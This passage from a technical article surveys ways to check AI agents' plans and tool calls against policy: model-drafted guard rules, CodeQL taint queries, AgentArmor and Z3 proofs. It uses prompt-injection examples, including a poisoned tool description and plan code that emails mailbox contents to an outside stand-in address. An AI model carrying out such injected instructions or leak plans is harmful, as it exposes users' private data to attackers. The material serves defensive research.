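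They then examined three benchmarks and found that ordinary program code could enforce 93 of the 126 requirements, or 74%. The share was 42 of 51 for τ²-bench, 17 of 18 for an in-car voice assistant and 34 of 57 for an assistant that handles medical records. The medical benchmark had no policy, so the researchers had language models write one. Excluding that benchmark raises the share to 59 of 69, or 86%. The researchers judged enforceability themselves and regard their figure as a lower bound because their list of techniques may be incomplete.

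Of the 93 enforceable requirements, 88 need only simple checks, such as confirming that a ticket belongs to the user before cancelling it. The other five, all in the medical policy, require analyzing data flow or the order of calls. The rule about Michelle's mailbox is of this second kind, which is rare in these benchmarks. Such rules may be more common in offices, since four of the five benchmarks with general verifiable rules cover customer service, where most rules concern who is entitled to what.

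Code can't enforce requirements such as speaking in a neutral tone or not inventing facts. It also can't enforce requirements that depend on judgment, such as not offering compensation "unless the user explicitly asks for it". A designer could replace this one with a cruder rule that blocks the compensation tool until the user types the exact word "compensation". Code can enforce that rule, but it will frustrate anyone who asks for their money back in other words.

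When the rules were only in the prompt, agents broke code-enforceable ones in 20% to 78% of tasks. Enforcing those rules in code eliminated a large class of these violations, and task completion stayed the same or improved.

### Rules that a model drafts

The most direct approach is for an operator to write every rule in advance, as with guardians. The operator knows what each rule means, but has to translate a long policy document by hand and keep the translation up to date. Several groups have therefore had a model draft the rules. *Soteria* does this for rules about the order of calls, and *Towards Enforcing Company Policy Adherence in Agentic Workflows* (2025) describes a system that compiles policy documents into guard code for each tool, with encouraging but preliminary results on tau-bench's airline tasks. More detailed measurements are available for VeriGuard and NOMOS. Both are runtime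 monitors, but a gate for whole plans also needs rules and is subject to the same drafting errors.

*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) starts from a request in plain English, such as "The agent cannot send emails to non-company addresses". A model writes a Python function that allows or denies an action, along with a list of logical constraints it should satisfy. The system looks for ambiguities in the request and asks the user about them, or picks the most likely reading if no user is available. It then generates tests and revises the function until they pass. Finally, Nagini, a program verifier for Python, tries to prove that whenever the preconditions hold at the start, the postconditions hold at the end. If the proof fails, the model gets the error and tries again, up to a fixed number of attempts.

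The proof shows only that the function matches the constraints. A model wrote both, so the constraints may not match the user's request. If the model had formalized "non-company addresses" with Meijer's wildcard, Nagini could have proved the faulty function correct. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the user has to validate the constraints by hand. A second weak point arises at runtime, when another model extracts the function's arguments from the agent's inputs and outputs. An attacker who misleads that model about the recipient can get past a correct function.

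The researchers tested VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, which includes prompt injection, poisoned memory and hidden backdoors. Without a defence, attacks succeeded between 50% and 64% of the time on average, depending on the model. VeriGuard reduced this rate to zero for all four models. A much simpler defence, in which a model judges directly whether an action breaks the policy, also reduced it to zero, but task success was higher with VeriGuard, for instance 63.3% against 40.2% with Gemini 2.5 Flash.

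Much of that advantage may come from how VeriGuard responds to a violation rather than from better rules. With the same model, task success was 38.1% when VeriGuard blocked the agent's whole action, and 63.3% when it blocked only the suspicious tool call and told the agent which rule it had broken. The proof seems to have added little that the benchmark could measure, since attack success had already fallen to zero before that step. VeriGuard classified every case correctly in one access-control dataset and 95% to 97% of cases in another, where its errors were mostly denials of permitted actions.

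NOMOS gives the drafting model much less freedom. People first prepare a fixed vocabulary of conditions, each with its own code, including 34 for the three domains in τ²-bench. The compiler splits the policy into clauses, and a model matches each clause to a condition and a set of tools. The model does this five times, and the compiler keeps only the matches that win a majority. A deterministic program also checks each candidate rule for structural defects. At runtime, the rules rely only on tool results and the user's own messages, so an agent can't satisfy a rule by claiming that the user has approved something.

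Yu and colleagues found structural defects in 29 of 79 candidate rules for the airline (36.7%) and in 7 of 53 for a retailer (13.2%). Most of the defective rules combined real tools in ways that couldn't work, and none used an invented tool name. The retail policy requires the agent to authenticate the user at the start of a conversation. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool until the user was authenticated, including the two tools that perform authentication, so no customer could have got past it. In a separate experiment with all the checks switched off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not function.

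Some bad rules have no structural defect. A telecom company's policy required checking that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request, but the model produced a rule that forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue. To catch such rules, NOMOS replays recorded conversations in which an unprotected agent completed its task and counts how many of the agent's calls each rule would have refused. The faulty payment rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests. An operator could test a plan gate the same way, by running old, successful plans through a new policy.

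Replay can miss rarer mistakes. The airline policy forbids modifying basic economy flights but allows passengers on those fares to upgrade their cabin. The compiled rule blocked both. The researchers scored the system against independent, hand-written rules that contained the same mistake, so comparing the two couldn't reveal it. They found it only when another model reviewed individual refusals and they examined the disagreements.

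With NOMOS, violations of the encoded rules fell from 66.3% to 2.6% of the state-changing calls that ran in the airline tasks, and from 30.8% to 6.9% in the retail tasks. Task success rose from 39.2% to 47.6% for the airline and fell from 52.4% to 50.2% for the retailer, but neither difference was statistically significant on a single attempt. The airline agent made only a third as many state changes as it did without NOMOS. More than half of the remaining retail violations were of two clauses that the compiler had not turned into rules.

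The attack results come from AgentDojo. On the banking tasks, attacks succeeded in 46.5% of 288 cases without protection and in none with NOMOS. Three rules covered nine types of attack, mainly because most of the attacks try to pay someone the user never mentioned. In 8 cases, however, the agent sent an injected payment to someone already in the account's history, which the policy allows. On the other three sets of tasks, at most 3.6% of attacks succeeded. AgentDojo has no written policy, so the researchers wrote one for each set, which makes these results less convincing than the airline and retail ones.

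The drop in completion of harmless tasks varied widely. For banking, completion fell from 79.2% to 70.8%. For the workplace chat tasks, correcting one misdirected rule stopped all the attacks that had been getting through (15 of 105) but reduced completion of harmless tasks from 57.1% to 14.3%. These tasks often require the agent to act on names and addresses it has just read, like Bob's address in the CaMeL example, but the corrected rule accepts only targets that the user named.

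A model can also write a new policy for each request. Yu and colleagues ran Progent, which does this, on the same banking tasks, and 5.6% of attacks succeeded. Twelve of the sixteen successes came from two requests to pay a bill, neither of which named the recipient's account, so a policy derived from either request had nothing to check the account number against. NOMOS blocked the attacks in both tasks, but in one it also blocked the legitimate payment because that account number appeared only in the bill.

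### Contracts that the agent proposes

clauz3 has the agent propose the rule for its own program. This sounds like asking a burglar to write the alarm settings, but the agent gets much less control than that. According to clauz3's *Concepts*, a trusted engineer first describes the tools and defines a vocabulary of possible promises. The agent writes a program and chooses promises from the vocabulary. clauz3's prover checks that the program keeps them, and the user then accepts or rejects the promises without having to read the code.

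If the user asks the agent to send a greeting to Jie, for example, clauz3 shows three promises: the program emails only Jie's address, sends at most one message, and never emails the same address twice. For Michelle's request, an uncompromised agent could promise to send no email. An agent misled by a poisoned tool description would have to promise something weaker, such as emailing only the attacker's address, and Michelle would see that address before the program ran.

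The scheme works only if the user notices when a contract is too weak. clauz3's *FAQ* states that clauz3 does not prevent prompt injection and that a manipulated agent can still propose a weak contract. The agent can even choose `no_guarantees()`, which promises nothing, though it has to do so openly. A list of three promises is shorter than a program and more informative than a prompt to allow `send_email`, so users may be less likely to click "Allow" out of habit. An operator can also spare the user routine decisions by setting a policy that approves some contracts automatically, rejects others and refers the rest to a person.

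The vocabulary also limits what a contract can express. The vocabulary in clauz3's *Email example* has eight entries, which cover the recipients, the number of messages, their length and whether two people receive the same text, but not where the text came from. An agent using it could promise to email only colleagues, but could not promise to keep mailbox contents inside the company while letting other messages out. The engineer would have to add that promise, and would face the same decisions about "contents" and "leave" as an operator writing the policy in advance.

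clauz3 is a research experiment, not a finished product. Its tools also don't yet demand proof of the user's approval before they run. The arrangement suits personal tasks, where the user knows who should receive what. It suits company rules less well, because Michelle could approve a leak that her employer forbids.

### Checking the policy itself

A program can check a policy for mistakes, no matter who wrote it, before any agent relies on it. Two such programs became available to developers for languages that companies already use.

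Google released a verifier for CEL, its Common Expression Language, in August 2026. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) describes three kinds of check, all using Z3 to search for an input that the policy handles incorrectly. One kind, the equivalence check, compares two versions of a rule. In Google's example, an agent leaves out a pair of parentheses when rewriting a rule that allows ports 80 and 443 in production. The verifier finds that the new version also allows port 443 outside production.

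A validity check tests whether a condition holds for every input, which exposes gaps. For example, if an engineer assumes that every port is either above 1024 or at most 80, the verifier returns port 81 as a counterexample. The third check tests an invariant, a statement that must hold whenever certain assumptions do. In one example, the policy must refuse any request that has no approval and doesn't come from an administrator. The verifier finds that a privileged job can still get into production, because an earlier line of the policy allows it regardless of approval or who sent it.

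Google claims that every violation the verifier reports is real. If a possible violation depends on a custom function that the verifier has no model of, the verifier reports the result as inconclusive. It checks nested data only to a depth the user sets.

An invariant would catch the faulty wildcard in Meijer's rule. The operator could assert that the policy treats any address ending in `@valleysharks.com` as internal, and the verifier should return an address like Michelle's as a counterexample. Unlike a single test, this covers every such address. But an invariant can reflect the author's misunderstanding. The string `eve@example.org, bob@valleysharks.com` also ends in the right domain, so the invariant would require the policy to treat Eve as a colleague.

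Amazon's Cedar is a language for rules about who may do what to which resource. In *Prove It, Part 2*, Buliani, Chunawala and colleagues (2026) explain how Amazon's agent platform applies it to tool calls. A call is allowed only if at least one rule permits it and no rule forbids it. Conflicts between rules are therefore resolved predictably, though not always as the rule writer intended. If a prohibition covers everything that a permission allows, the permission has no effect.

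According to AWS, the platform runs two checks on these policies. The first compares each policy with a schema of the tools and their parameters, which would catch a name like `fetch_email`. The second turns each policy into a logical formula and looks for policies that allow everything, refuse everything or contain impossible conditions. A developer can write a rule in plain English, have a model translate it into Cedar and use these findings to correct the translation. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) describes a similar loop, in which a deterministic critic checks a model's drafts for syntax errors, schema violations and contradictions, then returns the drafts for revision.

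An operator should check that the second stage is on. According to AWS's *Policy create and update*, the schema check always runs when someone adds a policy directly, but the logical analysis runs only in `FAIL_ON_ANY_FINDINGS` mode, not in `IGNORE_ALL_FINDINGS` mode. The analysis covers the new policy together with all existing ones, which is necessary to find a permission that an older prohibition cancels.

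These general checks find policies that nobody could have wanted, but they can't detect a policy that looks sensible and differs from what the company wanted, such as one that allows refunds up to $500 when the limit is $50. To detect that, the checker needs a separate statement of the goal. *AutoCedar* (2026) includes a benchmark of 221 tasks, each with a description in prose and a fixed verification plan. The plan's reference policies include "floors" and "ceilings", presumably the least that a correct policy must allow and the most that it may allow. For the mailbox rule, the floor would include the email to Michelle's own address, and the ceiling would exclude the leak to an outsider. People still have to choose these limits, but listing a few things that must always or never happen is probably easier than writing a complete policy without mistakes.

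Cedar also decides one request at a time, from the facts it receives with the request. It can compare a recipient's domain with a list but can't work out whether the body of a message came from Michelle's mailbox. That fact has to come from an analysis of the plan.

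## Tracing private or untrusted data with CodeQL

Once the operator has written the mailbox rule, the gate has to check whether a given plan can break it. Taint analysis can do this by marking the value that a source returns and following it through each assignment and call to see whether it can reach a sink. Meijer suggests using CodeQL, GitHub's tool for finding security bugs in large programs. CodeQL can do far more than a three-line plan requires, but an operator has to build several supporting parts to use it.

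### From source code to a path query

According to GitHub's *About CodeQL*, CodeQL analyzes code in three steps. It builds a database from the source code, runs queries against the database, and presents the results as messages about particular places in the code. Each language has its own program, called an extractor, for building the database. The Python extractor reads the source files directly, while the extractors for compiled languages monitor the normal build. The database represents the program's syntax tree, control flow (which statement can run after which) and data flow (which values can end up where).

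The syntax tree becomes a set of tables. GitHub's *Code scanning and Ruby* (2022) gives a simplified layout, in which one table lists every expression, another names every call, and another links calls to their arguments. With words in place of numeric codes, `summarize_emails(emails_fetched)` would become:

```
expressions:     (7, call)   (8, variable)
calls:           (7, "summarize_emails")
call_arguments:  (7, 8, 0)
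```

The last row means that expression 8 is argument number 0 of call 7. Finding every call to `send_email` is then a table lookup.

Finding a leak also requires the data-flow graph. Its nodes are the parts of a program that carry values when it runs, and an edge means that a value may pass from one node to another. GitHub's *About data flow analysis* distinguishes ordinary data flow, which follows a value along these edges only while it stays the same, from taint tracking, which also follows values derived from it. For example, after `y = x + 1`, a tainted `x` makes `y` tainted too. The mailbox rule needs taint tracking because a summary is a different value from the emails it summarizes.

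A path query suits this rule. It defines the sources, the sinks and the steps that can connect them. CodeQL then reports each route it finds from a source to a sink.

### A query for the mailbox rule

Suppose a poisoned tool description has led the model to add a leak to Michelle's plan. Written in Python, with every argument passed by name, the plan is:

```python
import tools
emails_fetched = tools.fetch_mail()
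email_summary = tools.summarize_emails(emails=emails_fetched)
tools.send_email(to="eve@example.org", body=email_summary)
```

GitHub's *Analyzing data flow in Python* describes four predicates that a query's author can define: `isSource`, `isSink`, `isBarrier` and `isAdditionalFlowStep`. A query for the mailbox rule could use them like this:

```ql
/**
 * @name Mailbox contents sent outside the company
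 * @kind path-problem
 * @problem.severity error
 * @id gate/mailbox-leak
 */
import python
import semmle.python.dataflow.new.DataFlow
import semmle.python.dataflow.new.TaintTracking
import semmle.python.ApiGraphs

API::Node tools() { result = API::moduleImport("tools") }

module LeakConfig implements DataFlow::ConfigSig {
  // Source: whatever fetch_mail returns
  predicate isSource(DataFlow::Node n) {
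    n = tools().getMember("fetch_mail").getACall()
  }

  // Sink: the body of a message, unless the plan spells out
  // a single recipient at the company's own domain
  predicate isSink(DataFlow::Node n) {
    exists(DataFlow::CallCfgNode send |
      send = tools().getMember("send_email").getACall() and
      n = send.getArgByName("body") and
      not send.getArgByName("to").asExpr().(StringLiteral).getText()
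            .regexpMatch("[^@,;\\s]+@valleysharks\\.com")
    )
  }

  // Extra step: a tool's result depends on all its arguments
  predicate isAdditionalFlowStep(DataFlow::Node a, DataFlow::Node b) {
    exists(DataFlow::CallCfgNode call |
      call = tools().getAMember().getACall() and
      a = call.getArgByName(_) and
      b = call
    )
  }

  // Barrier: count_emails returns only a number
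  predicate isBarrier(DataFlow::Node n) {
    n = tools().getMember("count_emails").getACall()
  }
}

module Leak = TaintTracking::Global<LeakConfig>;
import Leak::PathGraph

from Leak::PathNode source, Leak::PathNode sink
where Leak::flowPath(source, sink)
select sink.getNode(), source, sink, "Mailbox contents leave the company."
```

For the poisoned plan, the search goes as follows:

```
tools.fetch_mail()                source
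  -> emails_fetched               assignment
  -> emails=emails_fetched        use as an argument
  -> tools.summarize_emails(...)  extra step
  -> email_summary                assignment
  -> body=email_summary           sink, because eve@example.org is outside
```

The route is complete, so the gate rejects the plan. If the message went to `michelle@valleysharks.com`, its body wouldn't count as a sink and the query would find nothing.

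The extra step serves the same purpose as the contract for `summarize_emails`. CodeQL has no source code for that tool, so without the step the route would stop at the tool's argument. A CodeQL tutorial by Tweag (2025), a software consultancy, addresses the same problem with sarge, a little-known Python library that runs system commands. CodeQL has no model of sarge, so its ready-made queries miss dangerous calls made through it. The query above avoids this problem by assuming that the result of every tool, including any the operator adds later, depends on all its arguments.

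That assumption causes false alarms. Barriers, also called sanitizers, remove some of them by stopping the tracking at certain points. Here the operator has decided that the number of emails in a mailbox isn't secret, so a plan may send the output of `count_emails` to anyone. CodeQL doesn't check that decision. If an operator marks a redaction tool as a barrier and the tool misses phone numbers, every plan that uses it can leak phone numbers.

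The query also requires the plan to contain the recipient's address as literal text. A more lenient version could trace a variable back to the addresses it might hold, but it should accept the message only if all of them are internal. If one internal address were enough, the query would accept a plan that sets the variable to Michelle's address in one branch and Eve's in the other, which could leak the message to Eve.

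### Can CodeQL query a JSON plan?

Meijer's plans are in JSON, which CodeQL can read but supports only partly. GitHub's *Supported languages and frameworks* lists `.json` among the file types for JavaScript. GitHub's *Class JsonValue* documents ways to move around a JSON file, such as getting the value of a named property, but lists nothing for data flow. CodeQL treats `emails_fetched` in one step's `result` field and in the next step's arguments as two equal strings. Only the plan's interpreter treats the second as a reference to the first.

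A query author can supply this connection:

```ql
// step b uses the result of step a
predicate feeds(JsonValue a, JsonValue b) {
  a.getPropValue("result").getStringValue() =
    b.getPropValue("function").getPropValue("arguments")
     .getPropValue(_).getStringValue()
}
```

In CodeQL's query language, `feeds+` applies the `feeds` relation one or more times, so it would link the fetching step to the sending step through the summary. But this query is a taint checker written from scratch. It ignores the order of steps, and it misses a reference inside a list because the list adds a level of nesting. Printing the plan as Python or JavaScript is usually better, since CodeQL's data-flow libraries then handle assignments, lists and branches.

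The operator also has to trust the printer. It must escape text correctly, or a quotation mark in an argument could end the string early and change the program. It must also preserve the meaning the plan has in the interpreter. If a plan assigns `email_summary` twice and the interpreter keeps the first value while Python keeps the second, CodeQL checks a different plan from the one that runs.

Operators can describe some tools without writing queries. GitHub's *Customizing Library Models for Python* explains how to do this in YAML, a text format for configuration files. For the summarizing tool, the entry would be:

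```yaml
extensions:
  - addsTo:
      pack: codeql/python-all
      extensible: summaryModel
    data:
      - ["tools", "Member[summarize_emails]",
         "Argument[emails:]", "ReturnValue", "taint"]
```

The last word means that the output derives from the input but may differ from it. A tool that returns its input unchanged would get `value` instead. Similar entries describe sources and sinks. Since version 2.25.2, YAML can also declare barriers and barrier guards (GitHub, *CodeQL now supports sanitizers and validators in models-as-data*, 2026). A barrier guard is a yes-or-no check, such as `is_approved(address)`. CodeQL stops tracking the checked value in the branch where the check succeeds.

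These entries can't fully express the mailbox rule. A sink entry names a function's argument and a kind of vulnerability, but has no field for a condition on another argument. It can mark the body of every message as a sink, but can't limit this to messages sent to outsiders. The check for outside recipients has to stay in the query.

A wrapper program then creates the database, runs the query and reads the results file. It must treat any error as a rejection. It should also confirm that the database contains as many tool calls as the plan has steps, because a query over an empty database finds no leaks even if the plan has one.

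### Time and licence

GitHub's published timings cover whole scans of ordinary repositories, not the database step alone. GitHub (2026) sorted more than 100,000 repositories into those that take less than three minutes to scan, three to seven minutes, and more than seven. A ten-line plan should take much less, but starting the tools and preparing the analysis take some time even for a short program. An operator should measure this delay before adding it to every user request. For code under 100,000 lines, GitHub recommends at least 8 GB of memory and two processor cores.

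Incremental analysis probably won't speed up the check much. GitHub (2026) announced it in June 2026 for the CodeQL CLI, the command-line version that a gate would use, and claims in *Using incremental analysis with the CodeQL CLI* that it makes scans up to ten times faster. But part of the saving comes from reusing a stored database of the existing code, and a newly written plan has hardly any existing code.

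The licence may be a bigger obstacle. According to GitHub's *CodeQL CLI*, the program is free to use on public repositories, but an organization needs a GitHub Team or Enterprise Cloud plan and a GitHub Code Security licence to use it on private ones. Anyone without that licence is bound by separate terms, whose August 2020 version allows academic research and the analysis of open-source code but not automated analysis of private code. That seems to rule out a gate that builds a database for every plan in a company's agent. The same version also forbids offering CodeQL to others as a hosted service, and the exemption it grants to paying customers doesn't mention this ban. A company that wants to sell an agent with CodeQL inside should therefore first ask GitHub whether it may, and how the licence treats plans that never enter a repository.

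### Semgrep or a purpose-built checker

Meijer also mentions Semgrep, another static analysis tool. Its rules are patterns that resemble the code they match, so `tools.fetch_mail()` can itself describe a source. Semgrep has a taint mode with sources, sinks and sanitizers, and it needs no database. Its free edition follows data only within a single function, which is enough for a short plan that defines no functions of its own. By default, Semgrep treats the result of a call as tainted if any argument is tainted, while CodeQL needs an explicit step for this. Forgetting to describe a tool in Semgrep is therefore more likely to cause a false alarm than a leak.

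For a small plan language, the operator can write a checker that reads the JSON directly:

```
labels = {}
for step in plan:
    contract = contracts[step.tool]         # no contract: reject
    inputs   = labels of each argument      # literal text has none
    contract.check(inputs, step.arguments)  # broken rule: reject
    labels[step.result] = contract.output(inputs)
```

In the poisoned plan, the contract for `fetch_mail` labels its result private, and the contract for `summarize_emails` copies that label to the summary. The email then has a private body and an outside recipient, which violates the contract for `send_email`, so the checker rejects the plan. The checker needs no printer, licence or database and visits each step once. The flow rules in guardians work this way.

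A small checker is probably the best choice for straight-line JSON plans, because it is short enough for one person to review completely. However, nobody else uses it, so nobody else will find its bugs, and branches and loops make it harder to write correctly. If plans are short Python programs, Semgrep is a sensible middle option. CodeQL is worth the effort when plans define functions, use classes or call ordinary libraries, or when a company already has the licence and people who write queries. A small checker would have to reproduce much of CodeQL to cover such programs.

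### Private data and untrusted data

Michelle's mailbox is private, but it is also untrusted because anyone can email her. Each property needs its own rule. A confidentiality rule stops private data from reaching people who shouldn't have it. An integrity rule stops untrusted data from controlling something important, such as a recipient or a payment amount. Both rules can use `fetch_mail` as their source, but the confidentiality rule's sink is the body of the outgoing message, while the integrity rule's sink is the recipient.

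| Plan | Confidentiality rule | Integrity rule |
|---|---|---|
| Send a mailbox summary to an outside address written in the plan | Reject | Accept |
| Take an address from an email and send it a fixed greeting | Accept | Reject |
| Take an outside address from an email and send it a mailbox summary | Reject | Reject |
| Send a mailbox summary to michelle@valleysharks.com | Accept | Accept |

The poisoned plan matches the first row. Eve's address came from a malicious tool description, but the integrity rule misses it because the address appears in the plan as literal text, which taint analysis normally treats as trusted. To catch it, the gate would have to compare the addresses in the plan with those in Michelle's request or her contacts.

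A message that mixes private and public text is private, and a value computed from trusted and untrusted data is untrusted. But a sanitizer for one rule may do nothing for the other. Checking that an address belongs to a colleague limits what an attacker can do with it, but doesn't make the message less private. Removing names from an email may make it safe to share, but the remaining text is still untrusted because the sender wrote it. An operator should therefore declare barriers separately for each rule. CaMeL's capabilities likewise record a value's sources separately from its permitted readers.

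### Cases that taint analysis gets wrong

A tool that calls a model is hard to describe precisely, because its output can reveal everything in the input without using any of the same words, as when it translates Michelle's emails into French. The only safe assumption is that the output depends on everything the model read. This causes false alarms, since a summary that reads "nothing urgent today" gets the same label as one that lists every deal.

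Restricting the model's answer to a few options helps more with integrity than with confidentiality. If the model can only answer yes or no, an attacker can't write an email that makes it return a new address. But if the question is whether any email mentions a merger, the answer reveals the secret. It may be reasonable to treat such a call as a barrier in the integrity rule, but not in the confidentiality rule.

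Taint analysis can also lose track of data that leaves the plan and comes back:

```python
emails = tools.fetch_mail()
tools.save_note(name="todo", text=emails)
note = tools.read_note(name="todo")
tools.send_email(to="eve@example.org", body=note)
```

The data passes from `emails` to `note` through the note-taking service rather than through the program, so the query above would miss this leak, even with its cautious assumption about tool results. The operator needs to add another extra step from saved note text to the result of `read_note`. Files, calendars and databases need the same treatment. If an earlier plan saved the note, no analysis of the current plan can find the connection, so it is safest to treat everything that `read_note` returns as private.

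An implicit flow reveals a secret without copying it:

```python
emails = tools.fetch_mail()
found = tools.mentions(emails=emails, text="merger")
if found:
    tools.send_email(to="eve@example.org", body="Lunch on Friday?")
```

The message is harmless, but Eve learns about the merger from its arrival. If she knows that the plan ran, she also learns something when no message arrives. The query finds no route because the message body is literal text. GitHub explains that an "if" statement has no node in the data-flow graph because it carries no value. Ten such tests could distinguish 1,024 states of the mailbox, and a loop that sends one fixed message per email would reveal how many emails there are.

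A purpose-built checker can close this gap by applying the label of a branch's condition to every call inside the branch and every variable that either side of the branch might change. In the example, `found` is private, so the checker rejects any message to an outsider that depends on it. The missed dependency in CaMeL's `approved` example is the same kind of gap. The stricter check also rejects some useful plans, such as "if the airline confirms my flight, text my brother". Michelle presumably wants her brother to know, so the policy would need an exception for recipients she names herself.

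Ordinary Python adds problems that a plan language can avoid. Two variables can refer to the same list:

```python
draft = ["Hello"]
message = draft
message.append(email_summary)
tools.send_email(to="eve@example.org", body=draft)
```

A checker that follows only names would miss the leak, because the plan changes `message` and sends `draft`. GitHub's guide includes this problem, aliasing, among the difficulties of building an accurate data-flow graph. CodeQL may also raise a false alarm when a plan sends only a harmless element of a list, because it records that the list contains a tainted element but not that element's position.

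In a dynamic call such as `getattr(tools, name)(body=email_summary)`, the program chooses the tool while it runs. CodeQL looks for the possible targets, but if `name` comes from an email, the target may not be known until the email arrives. A gate should refuse dynamic calls. If the plan language also forbids changing a value after it is created, aliasing becomes harmless. A short syntax check can enforce both restrictions before the taint analysis begins.

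CodeQL is therefore not sound for this rule, because an empty result means only that it found no route in its model of the plan. GitHub's guide describes several of these difficulties but gives no error rates. Rates from ordinary software would poorly predict CodeQL's accuracy on plans, because a large application calls many library functions, and CodeQL can miss a route through any function it has no model for. A plan calls perhaps a dozen tools, and the operator can describe them all. However, most of the data in Michelle's plan passes through one model call, so an error in that call's contract can change the verdict on every plan that uses the contract.

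### AgentArmor

Many agents never write a plan, so a gate has no program to analyse. *AGENTARMOR* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) instead treats the record of the agent's actions so far as the program. The system, developed at ByteDance, updates a graph of this record as the agent works and checks the graph before each tool call.

The graph has nodes for the user's request and for each tool call, its arguments and its result. Edges show which earlier text led the agent to choose a tool or an argument. In a plan, variable names supply these connections, but an ordinary agent chooses its next call after reading everything at once. AgentArmor therefore asks a language model which earlier texts influenced each choice. A registry of tools adds effects that the record doesn't show. For example, copying a code repository creates a local folder that inherits the repository's labels. The registry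 handles hidden connections like the one in the note-taking example.

AgentArmor then gives each node a confidentiality level and an integrity level, each low, medium or high. A node with several inputs takes the highest confidentiality and the lowest integrity among them. AgentArmor stops the agent if private data would flow to a less private place or if untrusted data would influence something that requires trust.

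On AgentDojo, AgentArmor reduced the share of successful attacks from 41% to 3%, while completion of harmless tasks fell only from 73% to 72%. Wang and colleagues compared it with two other defences:

| | Attacks succeeding | Harmless tasks completed | Running time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 41% | 73% | – |
| AgentArmor | 3% | 72% | 20.89 s |
| Progent | 2% | 64% | 11.24 s |
| CaMeL | 0% | 48% | 46.72 s |

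In a breakdown of nine types of attack, AgentArmor wrongly stopped 2% of non-malicious cases with GPT-4o and 8% with GPT-4o mini. The 72% completion rate applies only when nobody is attacking. AgentArmor abandons the whole task when it detects an attack, so an attacker who can't steal anything can still stop the agent from working. With GPT-4o, the agent completed 48% of tasks under attack.

AgentArmor keeps far more of the agent's usefulness than CaMeL does, because the agent can still read a result before choosing its next step, but its guarantee is weaker. Its type rules are deterministic, but a language model draws many of the graph edges they depend on. A missing edge has the same effect as a missing flow step in CodeQL. That model also reads the tools' results, including any injected instructions, so an attacker could try to influence it directly. Wang and colleagues acknowledge that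 they can't guarantee the model's reasoning. They call the system insensitive to adaptive attacks in one passage, but their ethics statement mentions vulnerabilities to them, and their reported experiments use AgentDojo's existing attacks. Drawing the graph takes about 70% of AgentArmor's running time, while the type system takes 1.13 seconds.

AgentArmor did worst on the attacks that the benchmark calls "direct", detecting only 40% of those that would have succeeded against GPT-4o. Only 4% of these attacks succeeded without AgentArmor, and 2% succeeded with it. The missed attacks involved requests such as reading a landlord's notice and following its instructions. AgentArmor treats the notice as trusted because the user told the agent to obey it. The operator can turn this setting off, which catches more attacks but also blocks more harmless tasks. A planner has the same difficulty with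 "do what the email asks", because tracing where an instruction came from doesn't show whether the user would have agreed to it.

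## Proving limits on arguments and effects with Z3

Taint analysis can show that a payment's amount came from a bill, but it can't show that the amount is at most $500 or which files a deletion will remove. Rules about such details depend on the actual values, many of which don't exist yet when the gate checks the plan. Meijer suggests checking these rules with Z3, an SMT solver from Microsoft Research. An SMT solver takes a formula with unknowns, such as numbers, text or arrays, and looks for values that make the formula true.

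### Searching for a violation

Hillel Wayne introduces Z3 with a school algebra problem. Given 4x + 2y = 14 and 2x − y = 1, Z3 returns "sat", short for satisfiable, and the solution x = 2 and y = 3. It returns "unsat" when no values fit and "unknown" when it can't determine which is the case.

A gate uses the same search to look for a way that a plan could break a rule. It combines the plan's steps, the contracts of the tools they call, and the negation of the rule into one formula, then runs Z3 to look for a case that satisfies all three. Such a case would be a run in which every tool meets its contract and the plan still breaks the rule.

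If Z3 returns "sat", its values describe a run that breaks the limit, and the gate rejects the plan with that counterexample as the reason. If Z3 returns "unsat", no such run exists in the model, and the gate accepts the plan. An "unsat" result covers every value the unknowns could take, which no set of tests can do, but it holds only for the model. If the contract for a payment tool leaves out a service fee, Z3's proof applies to a total without the fee, and the actual charge could exceed the limit.

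The gate should accept a plan only when Z3 returns "unsat". If Z3 returns "unknown" or times out, it has not determined whether the plan is safe, so the gate must reject the plan. A gate that rejected only on "sat" would accept any plan Z3 could not decide, so an attacker who could influence the plan could get it accepted by making it too hard to check.

### Four runs of the deletion example

In Meijer's example, a user asks an agent to delete foo.txt and bar.txt. The deletion tool accepts a wildcard pattern, so the model plans the single call `delete_file("*.txt")` instead of two separate calls. If the folder also contained notes.txt, the plan would delete that file too.

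Let `exists(f)` mean that a file is there before a call and `remains(f)` that it is there afterwards. For a plan with one call, there are four conditions to consider:

```
tool's effect:  ∀f.  f matches the pattern        ⇒ ¬remains(f)
tool's frame:   ∀f.  f doesn't match the pattern  ⇒ remains(f) = exists(f)
task's goal:    ¬remains(foo.txt) ∧ ¬remains(bar.txt)
task's frame:   ∀f.  f ∉ {foo.txt, bar.txt}       ⇒ remains(f) = exists(f)
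```

The tool's conditions are assumptions, and the task's conditions form the rule that the gate has to prove. This Python program lets an operator switch each frame condition on or off:

```python
from fnmatch import fnmatchcase
from z3 import And, Bool, BoolVal, Not, Solver, sat, unsat

FILES   = ["foo.txt", "bar.txt", "notes.txt", "a.pdf"]
TARGETS = ["foo.txt", "bar.txt"]

def check(plan, tool_frame, task_frame):
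    s = Solver()
    before = {f: BoolVal(True) for f in FILES}   # all four files exist
    now = before
    for i, pattern in enumerate(plan):           # one deletion per pattern
        after = {f: Bool(f"{f} after call {i + 1}") for f in FILES}
        for f in FILES:
            if fnmatchcase(f, pattern):
                s.add(Not(after[f]))             # tool's effect
            elif tool_frame:
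                s.add(after[f] == now[f])        # tool's frame
        now = after
    if s.check() != sat:                         # assumptions conflict
        return "reject"
    rule = [Not(now[f]) for f in TARGETS]        # task's goal
    if task_frame:
        rule += [now[f] == before[f] for f in FILES if f not in TARGETS]
    s.add(Not(And(rule)))                        # look for a violation
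    return "accept" if s.check() == unsat else "reject"
```

The wildcard plan is `["*.txt"]` and the correct plan is `["foo.txt", "bar.txt"]`. The verdicts are:

| Frame conditions | Wildcard plan | Correct two-call plan |
|---|---|---|
| None | Accept | Reject: the second call might bring foo.txt back |
| Tool only | Accept | Accept |
| Task only | Reject: notes.txt is gone | Reject: either call might delete anything |
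| Tool and task | Reject: notes.txt is gone | Accept |

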